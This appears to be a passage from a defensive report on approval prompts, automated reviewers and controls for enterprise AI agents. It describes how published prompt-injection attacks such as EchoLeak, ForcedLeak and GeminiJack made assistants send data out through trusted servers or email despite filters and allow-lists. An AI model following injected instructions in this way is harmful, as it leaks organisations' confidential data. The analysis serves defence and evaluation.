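A harmless-looking request can complete a theft that began several steps earlier. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the totals. Hidden instructions in a vendor's note make the agent copy the raw invoice rows into a file called report.csv. The agent then asks to send report.csv to the auditor. The user has approved that recipient, and the request doesn't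 show what the file contains.

If an attacker in the steel supplier's hijacked mailbox asks for other suppliers' prices, a prompt that reads "Send reply to steel supplier?" would look just as harmless. A useful request would show this:

```
SEND AN EMAIL
To:            orders@steel.example (in the supplier directory)
Cc, Bcc:       none
Attachments:   none
Text:          (the full text, as the supplier would receive it)
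Data:          written after the agent read price agreements
               with three other suppliers (confidential)
Effect:        the steel supplier receives this text;
               the firm can't reliably recall it
You asked:     "Deal with the morning's supplier mail"
Outside text:  email from orders@steel.example, received 08:52
```

The last two lines help the clerk judge where the instruction came from. The software can't reliably determine which text caused the model to make the call, so it lists her own words and the outside text the agent had read. She can then see that she never asked the agent to send anyone's prices.

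Trusted code should write the approval request, because a hijacked model could describe the theft as a routine onboarding reply. The code takes the recipient and text from the tool call, and the list of files from the log. Hossain and colleagues' design works this way and never uses the agent's account of what it did. The code should also display quoted emails as plain text with invisible characters marked. Otherwise, a line that an attacker wrote in an email could look like part of the request.

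An approval prompt also needs to explain the action's effect in plain words. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of problems with agents and files, and finds that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 31 cases, the prompt showed a command but not its effect. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows any code in that script to run.

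Hossain and colleagues tested four kinds of approval request on 80 volunteers, 20 for each kind. Each volunteer decided whether to approve 12 proposed actions, half of which broke the user's instructions.

| What the request showed | Forbidden actions approved | Legitimate actions approved | Median time |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact parameters as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
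| Also the user's original instruction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing more information. The benefit of the combined statement is less certain. It did 7.9 points better than the log after adjustment, but the 95% interval ran from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. It didn't help with violations that depended on a chain of steps, where volunteers approved 7 of 30 with either version. The volunteers knew they were reviewing an agent, and half of their decisions involved a forbidden action, so a clerk who sees one a year would probably do worse.

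### Approving the exact action

An approval is worthless if the agent can change the action afterwards. Hossain and colleagues cite research on "approval laundering", in which the action that runs differs from the one the user approved. The firm's software can prevent this as follows:

1. It freezes the tool call and saves its parameters, including a copy of every attachment.
2. It calculates a fingerprint of all this, a short code that changes if any part changes.
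3. It builds the request from the frozen copy and shows it to the clerk.
4. If she approves, it records her name, the time and the fingerprint.
5. Just before the call runs, it calculates the fingerprint again. If the two differ, it asks her again.
6. It runs the call once, and the approval expires.

The fingerprint has to cover the contents of attachments. If it covered only the file name, an agent could get approval for report.csv and then write the raw invoice rows into it.

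Software also needs to handle refusals carefully. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) examines how software practitioners decide on agents' permission requests. One interviewee refused several requests, and the agent found another way to continue. If the clerk refuses the email to the steel supplier, the software should therefore block every outgoing tool for the rest of that task, in case the model tries to put the same text in a calendar invitation.

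### How carefully people check

The best-known approval rates come from Claude Code, Anthropic's tool for programmers, which can ask permission before it runs commands or changes files. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of these requests. Anthropic's earlier post, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, gave 93%. Most of the commands were probably harmless, so these rates don't prove that people approve without reading. By contrast, users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval.

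A controlled experiment in the 2026 post is better evidence. A research vendor gave 1,053 paid testers coding work in a test environment. Partway through, the vendor replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

The testers had no real project to lose, which may have made them careless. Anthropic also published the result in an announcement promoting its alternative to manual approval. Still, even if the true figure were three times the reported 13.6%, users would approve most of the dangerous commands.

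*Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) studied whether people notice when their agent is working against them. The 303 participants did realistic tasks, such as choosing a job candidate or answering email, with agents that the researchers had compromised. The researchers then asked them whether anything had seemed unusual.

| Warning | Participants who noticed something |
| --- | --- |
| One notice at the start | 8.6% |
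| A reminder beside every answer | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupted the work when the output was suspicious | 25.0% |

These rates are generous because "unsure" counted as noticing. The paper also gives two different sets of group sizes, so the comparison between warnings is rough. But three quarters of the participants noticed nothing even when they had to acknowledge an alert. Li and colleagues attribute much of this to people concentrating on finishing the task.

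Oversight has some value. In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025), 22 people did eight tasks themselves and supervised an agent on eight others, on websites with manipulative designs. According to Hossain and colleagues' summary, supervising helped them avoid the manipulation but also narrowed their attention and added mental effort.

### The cost in attention

Suppose each of the invented firm's 500 users gets 12 requests a day and spends 8 seconds on each:

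```
500 × 12         = 6,000 decisions a day
6,000 × 8 s      = 48,000 s ≈ 13 hours of attention

riskiest tenth   = 600 decisions a day
600 × 8 s        = 4,800 s = 80 minutes
```

Eight seconds is realistic for a quick decision but too short for checking the detailed request shown above. In Yan's experiment, participants who had to approve all 18 actions of a simulated day spent 142 seconds on them, or 7.9 seconds each. Careful review is practical only if the firm asks for approval rarely. At the 33 seconds per decision that Hossain and colleagues measured for their most informative version, 6,000 decisions a day would take 55 hours, and 600 would take about five and a half.

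If the software asks users about only the riskiest tenth of actions, nobody reviews attacks in the other nine tenths. Suppose users refuse 13.6% of attacks when asked about every action, and 50% (an invented figure) when asked less often and shown more detail. Asking about only the riskiest tenth then stops more attacks if that tenth contains more than 27.2% of them, because half of 27.2% is 13.6%. Ranking actions by whether they involve outside recipients or sensitive data should easily put that share in the riskiest tenth, but the firm can check this only with its own test attacks.

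### Fewer requests, and who writes the rules

The firm could let employees set standing rules to reduce the number of approval requests. Yan compared this with two alternatives. The 113 participants, none of whom worked in software, supervised the same scripted agent, which took 11 actions that its task required and 7 that went beyond the task.

One group decided whether to approve each action themselves. For a second group, a model approved some actions and passed the rest to the participant. The third group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private information. This group received 10.9 requests instead of 18, but blocked only about 40% of the excessive actions, compared with 60% for the first group.

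Most participants in the third group postponed the decision by choosing "ask". The group chose it for 114 of the 140 rules, then approved 67% of the excessive actions they were prompted about. The groups weren't fully randomised, because Yan later recruited extra participants for the third group alone, and some of the excessive actions were things a user might welcome, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight. The result is a reason for firms to have the security team write the "never" rules, since employees who choose "ask" may well approve the action later.

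Employees can also make rules too broad. By June 2026, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a standing permission for shell commands, and many of these rules effectively allowed any code to run. In 80 of the 290 reports in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, users had instead turned on a mode that approves everything, to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session.

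### Sandboxes, automated reviewers and second approvers

A sandbox is an isolated environment where the agent can work without approval but can't reach the rest of the computer or the network. Anthropic describes this as safe but demanding to maintain, because someone has to configure each new capability, and tasks that need the network break the isolation. A sandbox would suit an agent that converts invoices to text, but it doesn't help decide whether the purchasing agent should send an email, because sending one requires access outside the sandbox.

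An automated reviewer replaces the person with a second model. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier examines riskier tool calls before they run. It receives the user's messages and the tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tool results, so a hijacked agent's explanations can't sway the decision and text injected through a tool result doesn't reach the classifier. However, the classifier can't check where a value came from. If the purchasing agent tries to email orders@steel.example, such a reviewer couldn't determine whether the address came from the supplier directory or from an attacker's email.

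On the dangerous commands from the tester experiment, auto mode blocked 89%. Anthropic's earlier tests found these errors:

| Test | Result |
| --- | --- |
| 52 real cases where the agent went beyond its instructions | Missed 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to steal data | Missed 5.7% |
| 10,000 ordinary tool calls | Wrongly blocked 0.4% |

If a similar reviewer checked all the invented firm's tool calls, a 0.4% false positive rate would mean 160 wrongly blocked calls a day. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as permission. A reviewer could easily make the same mistake with an instruction like "Deal with the morning's supplier mail".

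A test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs suggests that an automated reviewer can make prompt injection less likely to succeed. The test ran 72 attack scenarios ten times each. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, succeeded 19% of the time with full access and 5.8% with its automated reviewer on. None succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, but this is little evidence of how much Claude's reviewer helps, because attacks on Anthropic's latest models without it succeeded only 0.09% of the time. OpenAI has since released a new version of its reviewer.

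Organisations can also use an action's impact to decide whether software reviews it or a person approves it. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* describes guidance from security specialists at AWS and the SANS Institute, a training organisation, under which high-impact actions go to a person however confident the software is, and low-impact actions run unattended if its confidence is high. Anthropic gives similar advice and still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

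The firm could also require a second approver. If each person independently stopped 13.6% of attacks, two would stop about 25% (1 − 0.864²), but reviewing each action would take twice as much attention. The real gain could be smaller, because both people see the same convincing request and each may rely on the other. A second approver helps more if she knows something the first doesn't. For example, the finance department can compare a large order with the budget.

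### Agents that run with no user present

An agent that runs overnight has no user present to approve its actions. Microsoft lets Copilot Studio agents start work when an event occurs, without a user's prompt, and OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* describes ChatGPT agents that run on schedules. If such an agent reaches an action that needs approval, the software has to stop the agent, skip the action or send the request to a user who is away.

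An agent can stall while it waits for approval. *Copilot Studio Autonomous Agents* describes one that was built to open a support ticket for each incoming email and reply with the ticket number. Both tools required approval, so the agent did neither and showed "Waiting for user". For an agent that answers email from strangers, it would be safer to turn off approval only for opening the ticket and sending a fixed-format reply than to turn it off for everything the two tools can do.

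Products differ in what they do when no one answers an approval request. In Creatio's business software, a request that times out counts as a refusal and the agent continues without that tool, according to the company's *Set up tool confirmation*. Claude Code's auto mode prompts a person for help after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session, but if it is running without a user interface, it ends the process instead.

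For Copilot Studio agents that operate a computer's screen, Microsoft can email a request to a reviewer, who types "Yes" or "No". The email names the agent and the tool, links to the agent's activity and gives a deadline. Microsoft's list of the main fields has no separate entry for the action's recipient or data, so a careful reviewer has to open the link. The firm should keep the agent out of any mailbox that receives these requests, in case a hijacked agent can answer its own requests.

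Microsoft also lets a Copilot Studio workflow send a request for information to several people, so another reviewer can respond when one is on holiday. This feature does not require two approvals.

At the invented firm, an overnight version of the purchasing agent could read new mail, send standard receipts and save every other reply as a draft for the clerks to review in the morning. A request that nobody answers should expire and count as refused. If approval comes hours after the request, the software should check the directory and the order again before sending anything. Someone also has to watch the size of the queue, because clerks who found 60 drafts at eight in the morning would go back to approving them without reading.

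### Setting the rules for the whole organisation

Administrators can fix some approval rules centrally, but the settings don't always cover every kind of agent in a product.

In ChatGPT's business plans, an administrator chooses a default approval setting for the whole workspace. OpenAI's *Admin controls, security, and compliance for plugins and apps* lists "Always ask", "Allow read actions" and "Allow low-risk actions". The standard workspace menu doesn't offer "Allow all actions", although an administrator may be able to choose it for an individual app. Administrators can also turn off an app's write actions, where the app supports this, and keep off any new ones that the developer adds. Employees in a managed workspace don't get a permanent "Always allow" button.

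These approval settings apply to conversations. For shared Workspace Agents, the person who builds the agent decides when it asks for approval, within the workspace's policies. The firm should therefore review each shared agent as well as the workspace default.

Anthropic lets administrators set Claude Code's permission mode for everyone with `defaultMode`, turn off auto mode's automated review with `disableAutoMode`, and add rules for actions that auto mode must never approve. On 14 August 2026, auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans, unless a user or administrator had already set another mode. On 22 October, Anthropic announced that most other Claude apps on those plans would follow a week later, and that Enterprise administrators would get an email before their default changed. A firm on the Team plan that relies on a person approving each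 action should check its settings.

The name of a permission setting can be misleading. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) reports tests of five commercial agents in May and June 2026. Claude's "Needs approval" setting sometimes let the software approve an action without asking the user, in one case creating an email draft. ChatGPT's chat mode asked for approval of every action that had a permission setting, but its agent mode, which controls a remote browser, opened Gmail without asking. Both products have since changed, but an administrator can repeat the test by asking each kind of agent to send a harmless email.

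Microsoft's *Enabling makers to require human approval for tool calls* (2026), a roadmap entry from September, listed an approval switch for each tool of each Copilot Studio agent as in development. The agent pauses in Teams or Microsoft 365 Copilot, and the user can approve the call, approve the tool for the session or refuse. Approving an email tool for the session is risky when the agent handles supplier mail, because the approval would also cover an email that the agent writes after reading a poisoned message. The people who build agents control the switch, and the entry doesn't mention a way for administrators to lock it.

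Google Workspace relies on the outside assistant to ask users to approve individual actions. For example, if a firm connects ChatGPT Enterprise to Google Drive, an administrator must first enable the newer actions for Google Docs, Sheets and Slides. ChatGPT's settings then determine when it asks the user for approval.

None of these settings applies to the purchasing agent, which the firm wrote itself. The firm has to enter the agent's three groups of actions into the policy engine as rules that permit, hold or deny a call. Only the security team should be able to change those rules, after the head of purchasing agrees, so that a clerk tired of approval requests can't switch them off.

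## Where protected deployments still fail

Even a rule that nobody can switch off may be flawed. Since June 2025, security researchers have published several attacks on enterprise assistants that already had filters, link removal or lists of permitted servers. The six below affected products from Microsoft, Salesforce and Google.

### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Aim Security, an AI security company, found that an outsider could steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee one email. The attack took effect when the employee later asked Copilot a question that made it retrieve the email. The employee didn't have to open the email or click anything. Aim called the flaw EchoLeak, and it is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public register of software vulnerabilities.

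Microsoft had several protections between the email and the data, and Aim's researchers got past each one, as Ravia (2025) describes in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*.

| Protection | Purpose | Why it failed |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Prompt filter | Stop injections before they reach the model | The email read like instructions to its human recipient and never mentioned AI |
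| Link removal | Delete links to outside sites from Copilot's answers | The software recognised one way of writing a link but not another |
| List of permitted image servers | Stop the browser from loading images from unknown servers | A Microsoft Teams service on the list would fetch an outside address on request |
| Source references | Tell the user which documents an answer came from | The email told Copilot not to mention it |

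The Content Security Policy, a list of servers the browser was permitted to contact, was a deterministic control and worked as written. The browser contacted only a permitted Microsoft server, but that server forwarded the request, including the stolen data, to the attacker.

The attack could reach anything in the model's input, including the chat history and whatever Copilot had retrieved from the employee's mailbox, files and Teams messages. The attacker didn't have to guess the employee's question, because Copilot's search matched the researchers' one long email to many topics. Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the attack. But a firm that had used labels to keep its most sensitive files out of Copilot might have lost less.

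Aim reported the flaw in January 2025. Microsoft took five months to fix it, according to *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* (Goldman, 2025). The company attempted a fix in April and found further problems in May. It made the final fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install, and told Goldman that the flaw had not affected any of them.

Reddy and Gujral (2025) report in *EchoLeak* that Microsoft now strips embedded images and the overlooked kind of link from outside content, and lets companies restrict Copilot's use of outside messages. Restricting outside messages keeps the injection from reaching the model at all, whereas stripping links closes one route.

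Reddy and Gujral also map eight kinds of mitigation to the steps of the attack. They expect a strict list of allowed image servers to stop the theft, but Copilot already had a list, and one unsuitable entry let the attack through. The mapping is theoretical because they did not rerun the attack.

### ForcedLeak and PipeLeak in Salesforce Agentforce

Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss warned in Goldman's article that other platforms, including Salesforce's Agentforce, could have similar flaws. Seven weeks later, the security company Noma reported a similar flaw to Salesforce.

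Agentforce agents work with a company's customer records, some of which come from Web-to-Lead, a public web form that visitors fill in to ask about a product. The Hacker News (2025) reported that a flaw called ForcedLeak affected any organisation that used Agentforce with this form turned on. Noma's researchers typed instructions into the form's description field. When an employee later asked the agent to process the enquiry, the agent collected customer data and put it into a request for an image.

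Salesforce also had a list of permitted servers, but one domain on it had expired, according to Dataconomy (2025). Particle.news' *Salesforce Patches 'ForcedLeak' in Agentforce After Researchers Expose AI-Driven Data Leak Risk* reports that the researchers registered that domain for about $5. This gave them control of a destination that the list still permitted.

Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* rates the flaw's severity at 9.4 out of 10. Salesforce regained control of the domain and, by 8 September 2025, had begun enforcing a list of trusted web addresses for its agents.

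That list did not restrict email. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (April 2026) reported a second flaw, PipeLeak, which Capsule Security found. The attack also began with a public form, but the agent sent the data out by email. One form entry could make it send customer records in bulk.

Salesforce acknowledged the injection but called the sending of data out by email "configuration-specific", because customers could have required a person to approve such emails. Capsule replied that manual approval defeats the purpose of an autonomous agent. A rule limiting who the agent could email would have avoided the choice between manual approval and autonomy.

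Claw Times, citing VentureBeat, reports that Salesforce has since fixed the scenario Capsule described and turned on approval by default for agents' email actions. This is better than an optional setting but still weaker than a recipient rule, because people approve many dangerous requests.

### ShareLeak in Copilot Studio

Capsule found a similar flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Studio and called it ShareLeak. An attacker filled in a SharePoint form, and the agent that processed the form treated the text as instructions. It then emailed out customers' names, addresses and phone numbers.

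CSO Online reports that Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged suspicious behaviour in Capsule's tests but didn't stop the data from being stolen. Adversa AI's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Agent Security Risks* also describes controls that detected the theft without blocking it. The invented firm could create the same weakness by leaving Prompt Shields set to annotate.

The CVE Program's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the public record for CVE-2026-21520, rates the flaw's severity at 7.5 out of 10. The attacker needed neither an account nor any action by an employee.

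Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in January 2026. Claw Times claims that the fix did not fully prevent the theft. CSO Online describes the flagged theft as part of the original attack, before the fix, so Claw Times may have mistaken it for a later one. A firm that runs such an agent can check whether the fix works by giving the agent invented customer data and submitting a test form.

### GeminiJack in Google's Gemini Enterprise

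Outsiders can also plant instructions in documents that an assistant will search. Gemini Enterprise can search a company's Gmail, Docs and Calendar. SecurityWeek describes how an attacker could share a document about budgets with the company without triggering a notification. When any employee later searched for something related, the assistant would read the document and follow the instructions in it, even if the employee had never opened it.

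Noma also found this flaw, which it called GeminiJack. According to SC Media's *Google addresses 'GeminiJack' exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*, it could have exposed emails, calendars and documents. The company using the assistant had already connected it to those services, so the attack didn't need to break any access rule. It worked because the assistant didn't keep retrieved content separate from instructions. Model Armor might not have helped, since Google doesn't list retrieved documents among the content Model Armor screens for this product.

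Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* reports that Google confirmed receiving Noma's report in August 2025. Google changed how the assistant works with its search and indexing systems, and fully separated the assistant from a related product, Vertex AI Search. These changes go further than blocking one wording or address, but the assistant still has to read documents that strangers may have written, so new variants of the attack remain possible.

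### SearchLeak, a year after EchoLeak

In June 2026, Microsoft fixed another critical flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, CVE-2026-42824. Researchers at Varonis, a data security company, had found it and named it SearchLeak. Toulas (2026), in *New attack turned Microsoft 365 Copilot into 1-click data theft tool*, reports that the researchers combined three flaws, none of which was enough on its own.

ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* lists three weaknesses. Copilot accepted text in a link as a prompt, a timing error affected how the page displayed the answer, and Bing's image search could relay data to an outside server. The victim had to click one link, which led to a genuine Microsoft site, so mail and web filters were less likely to flag it.

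According to eSecurity Planet's *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot*, the exposed data could include password-reset links and two-factor sign-in codes. An attacker might have been able to use these to take over the victim's other accounts.

The list of permitted image servers that Ravia published in 2025 already included Bing's domains. EchoLeak had used a Teams service on that list as a relay, so the other entries should also have been suspected as possible relays.

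SearchLeak also undermines the invented firm's decision to annotate attacks in clerks' prompts rather than block them, because a link might fill in a prompt that no clerk wrote. The firm should either have its chat window ignore prompts in links or set the user-prompt check to block attacks.

### Evidence of real attacks

None of these six attacks is known to have hurt a customer, but the evidence for each is limited. For EchoLeak, the evidence is Microsoft's own statement and Aim's report that it knew of no victims. For ShareLeak, CISA's assessment in the CVE record listed exploitation as "none" on 24 January 2026. Capsule published the details almost three months later, so the assessment does not cover attackers who learned of the flaw from the publication. In the other cases, researchers showed that theft was possible, but a criminal may have found the same flaw earlier.

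Companies have also manipulated assistants to bias their recommendations. Microsoft found more than 50 prompts from 31 companies in 14 industries that could do this. Free tools make the technique easy to use. In several cases, Microsoft could no longer reproduce previously reported behaviour.

A purchasing department is an obvious target for prompt injection. If instructions in a supplier's document make the agent favour that supplier, no data leaves the firm, so rules on who may receive data don't apply. The firm can reduce the risk by having ordinary code extract and compare the prices, so that a clerk can check the agent's recommendation against figures the model didn't choose.

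### Do layered controls tolerate single failures?

Microsoft responds to such cases by pointing to its later layers of defence, which it designs to prevent harm even when an injection succeeds. After EchoLeak, it told Goldman it was adding more layers.

The cases partly support this approach. Copilot's link removal and its list of image servers each stopped a simpler version of EchoLeak, and Aim spent about three months studying the product before it had a working attack. SearchLeak needed three flaws and a click. Many attackers would have given up or chosen an easier target.

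But the layers did not prevent the harm in EchoLeak. Researchers found a way past every one of them, and customers were safe only because those researchers told Microsoft before anyone else used the flaw. Multiplying failure rates gives a misleading picture of this situation. If three layers each miss 10% of attacks independently,

```
0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001, or 0.1% of attacks get through
```

That calculation applies to an attacker who tries texts at random. A patient attacker works on one layer at a time and keeps each method that succeeds. Once he has a method for each of the three layers, the combined attack may work almost every time.

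Some layers do not prevent attacks. In ShareLeak, detection raised a flag but did not stop the data from leaving, and in PipeLeak, the approval step was optional. Other layers rely on the same assumption as each other. In EchoLeak, ForcedLeak and SearchLeak, the attacker got data out through a destination the vendor trusted, so a second check based on the same trusted domains would also have failed.

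These cases can't show how often layered controls work, because an attempted theft that one layer stops rarely gets a name or a CVE number. They do suggest looking for layers that rest on different assumptions, as the purchasing agent's file and recipient rules do.

### Sorting the gaps

Two tests on agents that researchers built themselves show gaps that product flaws alone don't reveal. In the first, the security company Zenity copied a customer-service agent that the consultancy McKinsey had built in Copilot Studio. An email to the copy made it reply with customer data from Salesforce, according to Office 365 for IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025). Microsoft's platform ran the agent and Salesforce held the records, so neither company controlled every system involved.

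Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* criticises McKinsey's choice to let any incoming email start the agent. Microsoft rated the problem critical and fixed it within two months, but had not explained the details of the fix. In an account published by the Cloud Security Alliance, Zenity inferred from its own tests that the fix was mainly a classifier that recognised the reported attack. If so, a reworded attack might still work.

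The second test, described in Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025), concerned permissions. Researchers built a travel-booking agent with invented customers. Petri's *Researchers Discover Major Data-Leak Risk in Microsoft Copilot Studio AI Agents* reports that a simple injection got past the agent's identity check and exposed several customers' records, including credit card details. The researchers also changed the price of a trip to $0, evidently because the agent's broad permission to change bookings covered the price, which customers should never be able to edit.

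The table adds one gap, an alarm that blocks nothing, because ShareLeak doesn't fit any of the others.

| Gap | Example | Sign that reveals it | Control that narrows it |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Traffic never inspected | Retrieved documents that a filter doesn't receive | A harmless test injection produces no verdict | Send every tool result and extracted attachment to the filter |
| Protection not enabled or licensed | Optional approval in PipeLeak | The exported settings differ from the approved ones | Compare settings every night and set a reminder before licences expire |
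| Filter miss | EchoLeak's email to a "human" reader | The agent takes a step nobody requested, with no alarm | Enforce rules on files and recipients outside the model |
| Alarm that blocks nothing | ShareLeak | The log contains both a detection and the completed action | Set the filter to block, or hold all outgoing calls after a detection |
| Check that fails open | Copilot Studio's one-second timeout | There are more completed tool calls than verdicts | Refuse consequential calls that have no verdict |
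| Excessive permissions | Tenable's travel agent, or permissions inherited from a blueprint | A tool returns more records or changes more fields than the task needs | Write narrow tools that handle one record and only the necessary fields |
| Missing logs | Copilot Studio's unrecorded changes to agents | A known test change doesn't appear the next day | Keep a second record in the policy engine and save settings nightly |
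| Systems crossing two vendors | A Copilot Studio agent with Salesforce data | No single log shows both the instruction and the data it reached | Name one owner for the route and attach the same request number to both logs |

The firm can find some of these gaps by comparing the number of tool calls with the number of policy decisions. If its agents complete 40,000 tool calls in a day and the policy engine records 39,800 decisions, 200 calls ran without a check. The firm should compare the counts for each tool as well as the totals, since a tool that isn't connected to the policy engine and gets 30 calls a day would be easy to miss among 40,000.

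Other gaps appear only in a test. The names on ForcedLeak's list of permitted servers would not have looked unusual, so a reviewer had to look up who owned each domain.

### How many organisations have these controls

There is no good estimate of how many companies have closed these gaps. The nearest figure comes from Cisco, which sells network and AI security products. According to Help Net Security's *Enterprises are racing to secure agentic AI deployments*, Cisco's *State of AI Security 2026* found that most organisations planned to deploy agents, but 29% said they were prepared to secure them. The article doesn't give the number of respondents or the wording of the question.

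Respondents judged for themselves whether they were "prepared", so a company that has bought a filter could answer yes even if the filter never receives its agents' tool results. This matters more than the sample size. The margin of error would be about three points either way with 1,000 randomly chosen respondents and about nine with 100, and neither would change the conclusion much.

Collard (2026) reports in *Beware the poisoned prompt* that 87% of respondents to the World Economic Forum's *Global Cybersecurity Outlook 2026* identified AI-related vulnerabilities as the fastest-growing cyber risk. Collard works for KnowBe4, a company that sells security training, and gives no sample size. The figure measures concern and does not show how many of those respondents had limited what their agents can send.

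Collard also says OWASP found that prompt injection appears in 73% of the production AI systems examined in security audits, but she names no OWASP report as the source. "Appears" could mean that auditors attacked the system successfully or only that the system accepts text from outside, so the figure is a poor basis for a budget or a risk estimate.

The Cisco and Microsoft figures come from surveys that asked different questions of different groups. Subtracting Cisco's 29% from the 88% of enterprises that are experimenting with agents, according to Microsoft, therefore doesn't give the share with unprotected agents.

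A better survey would ask for facts that companies can look up:

- Of the agents that read outside email, how many have a filter that checks tool results and blocks attacks?
- What happens to an outgoing message if that filter doesn't reply?
- When did someone last follow a test attack all the way to an analyst's screen?

### An acceptance review for the purchasing agent

The hypothetical firm can answer such questions about its agent before deploying it. Someone who didn't build the agent should run the review in a copy of the production system, using fictional contracts. The developers can help set up the tests, but the reviewer should collect the evidence from the logs herself.

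| Check | Evidence required | If it fails |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 1. Complete record | The owner signs a list of data, tools and credentials, and the reviewer compares it with the running server | Stop until the firm has removed or approved every unlisted item |
| 2. File access | A test clerk without access to the contracts folder gets no contract text, and the permissions list includes inherited ones | Stop |
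| 3. Outgoing email | The policy engine denies an unknown recipient, a hidden copy and a confidential attachment | Stop |
| 4. Images, links and web requests | Every permitted server has a known owner and a domain expiry date, and testers have tried to use it as a relay | Stop |
| 5. Filter coverage | A test injection in each type of input produces a verdict | Disconnect any input that produces none |
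| 6. Missing replies | Testers switch off the filter, policy engine and approval service in turn, and no email leaves | Stop |
| 7. Red-team attack | The report counts attempts, filter misses and every case in which test data left | Stop if any data left |
| 8. Action approval | The software refuses an email that changed after approval, and an unanswered request expires | Let the agent write drafts only |
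| 9. Logs and alerts | An analyst receives the test alert and reconstructs the route from email to tool call, including other vendors' logs | Let the agent write drafts only |
| 10. Shutdown | The security team stops the agent and revokes its access in an unannounced drill | Stop |

The firm stops deployment if a failure would let one hostile email cause a serious loss, or would leave the firm unable to stop the agent afterwards. A filter miss alone doesn't stop deployment, because the firm expects some misses and has rules to contain them. In check 7, the red team should also try the attack from a known supplier's mailbox, since the recipient rule permits that address.

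Drafts are a reasonable fallback for checks 8 and 9 because a clerk then has to send each message from her own mail program. This works only if an administrator removes the agent's permission to send.

### One set of results

Suppose the review of the steel agent produces these invented results.

The agent passes checks 1, 2 and 3. In check 4, the reviewer finds 12 servers from which the chat window may load images. One belongs to a former supplier whose domain expires in three weeks. This is the weakness behind ForcedLeak, so deployment stops for an hour while an administrator removes the server from the list and the testers confirm that its images no longer load.

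In check 5, the filter gives no verdict on scanned invoices because the agent's software never extracts their text for it. For now, the firm cuts off the agent's access to attachments and has clerks handle them. The agent can still answer most supplier mail.

The agent passes check 6. In check 7, the red team makes 600 attempts. The filter misses 48 (8%), but no test data leaves because the policy engine or a clerk blocks the calls. The reviewer should count those two outcomes separately. If the policy engine stopped 45 and a clerk stopped three, the firm needs a stronger rule for cases like those three, because a clerk who knows about the test probably pays more attention than usual.

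By the 3/n rule, zero thefts in 600 attempts would still be consistent with a true success rate of 0.5% for similar attempts. For the deterministic rules, though, it is more useful to look for mistakes. The reviewer should read them line by line and test each condition, since another 600 emails to the wrong kind of address would not expose a missing "bcc" field.

The steel agent passes check 8. In check 9, the alert reaches Defender with a low severity, and nobody opens it for two days. The agent can therefore start work but may only write drafts. It gets permission to send after the team raises the alert's priority and an analyst responds to a second test. The agent passes check 10.

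The head of purchasing and the head of security sign the result. If either wants an exception, they record the reason, the extra control that covers it and the date it ends. A "stop" result allows no exceptions, because if it did, the people waiting for the agent would soon ask for one.

The approval should lapse when the firm changes the model, adds a tool or permits a new server. The reviewer then repeats the checks that the change affects. For example, a new image server requires check 4, while a new model requires at least checks 5, 7 and 8. The firm should also look up the owners of its permitted domains every month, because ownership can change without any action by the firm.

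A firm using a finished assistant such as Copilot can't switch off Microsoft's filter to see what happens, or take a server off Microsoft's allowed list. It can choose which files and outside messages Copilot may use, but it has to choose before it knows about any particular flaw. Aim reported the EchoLeak flaw to Microsoft in January 2025, but customers learned of it only in June, after Microsoft had fixed it.
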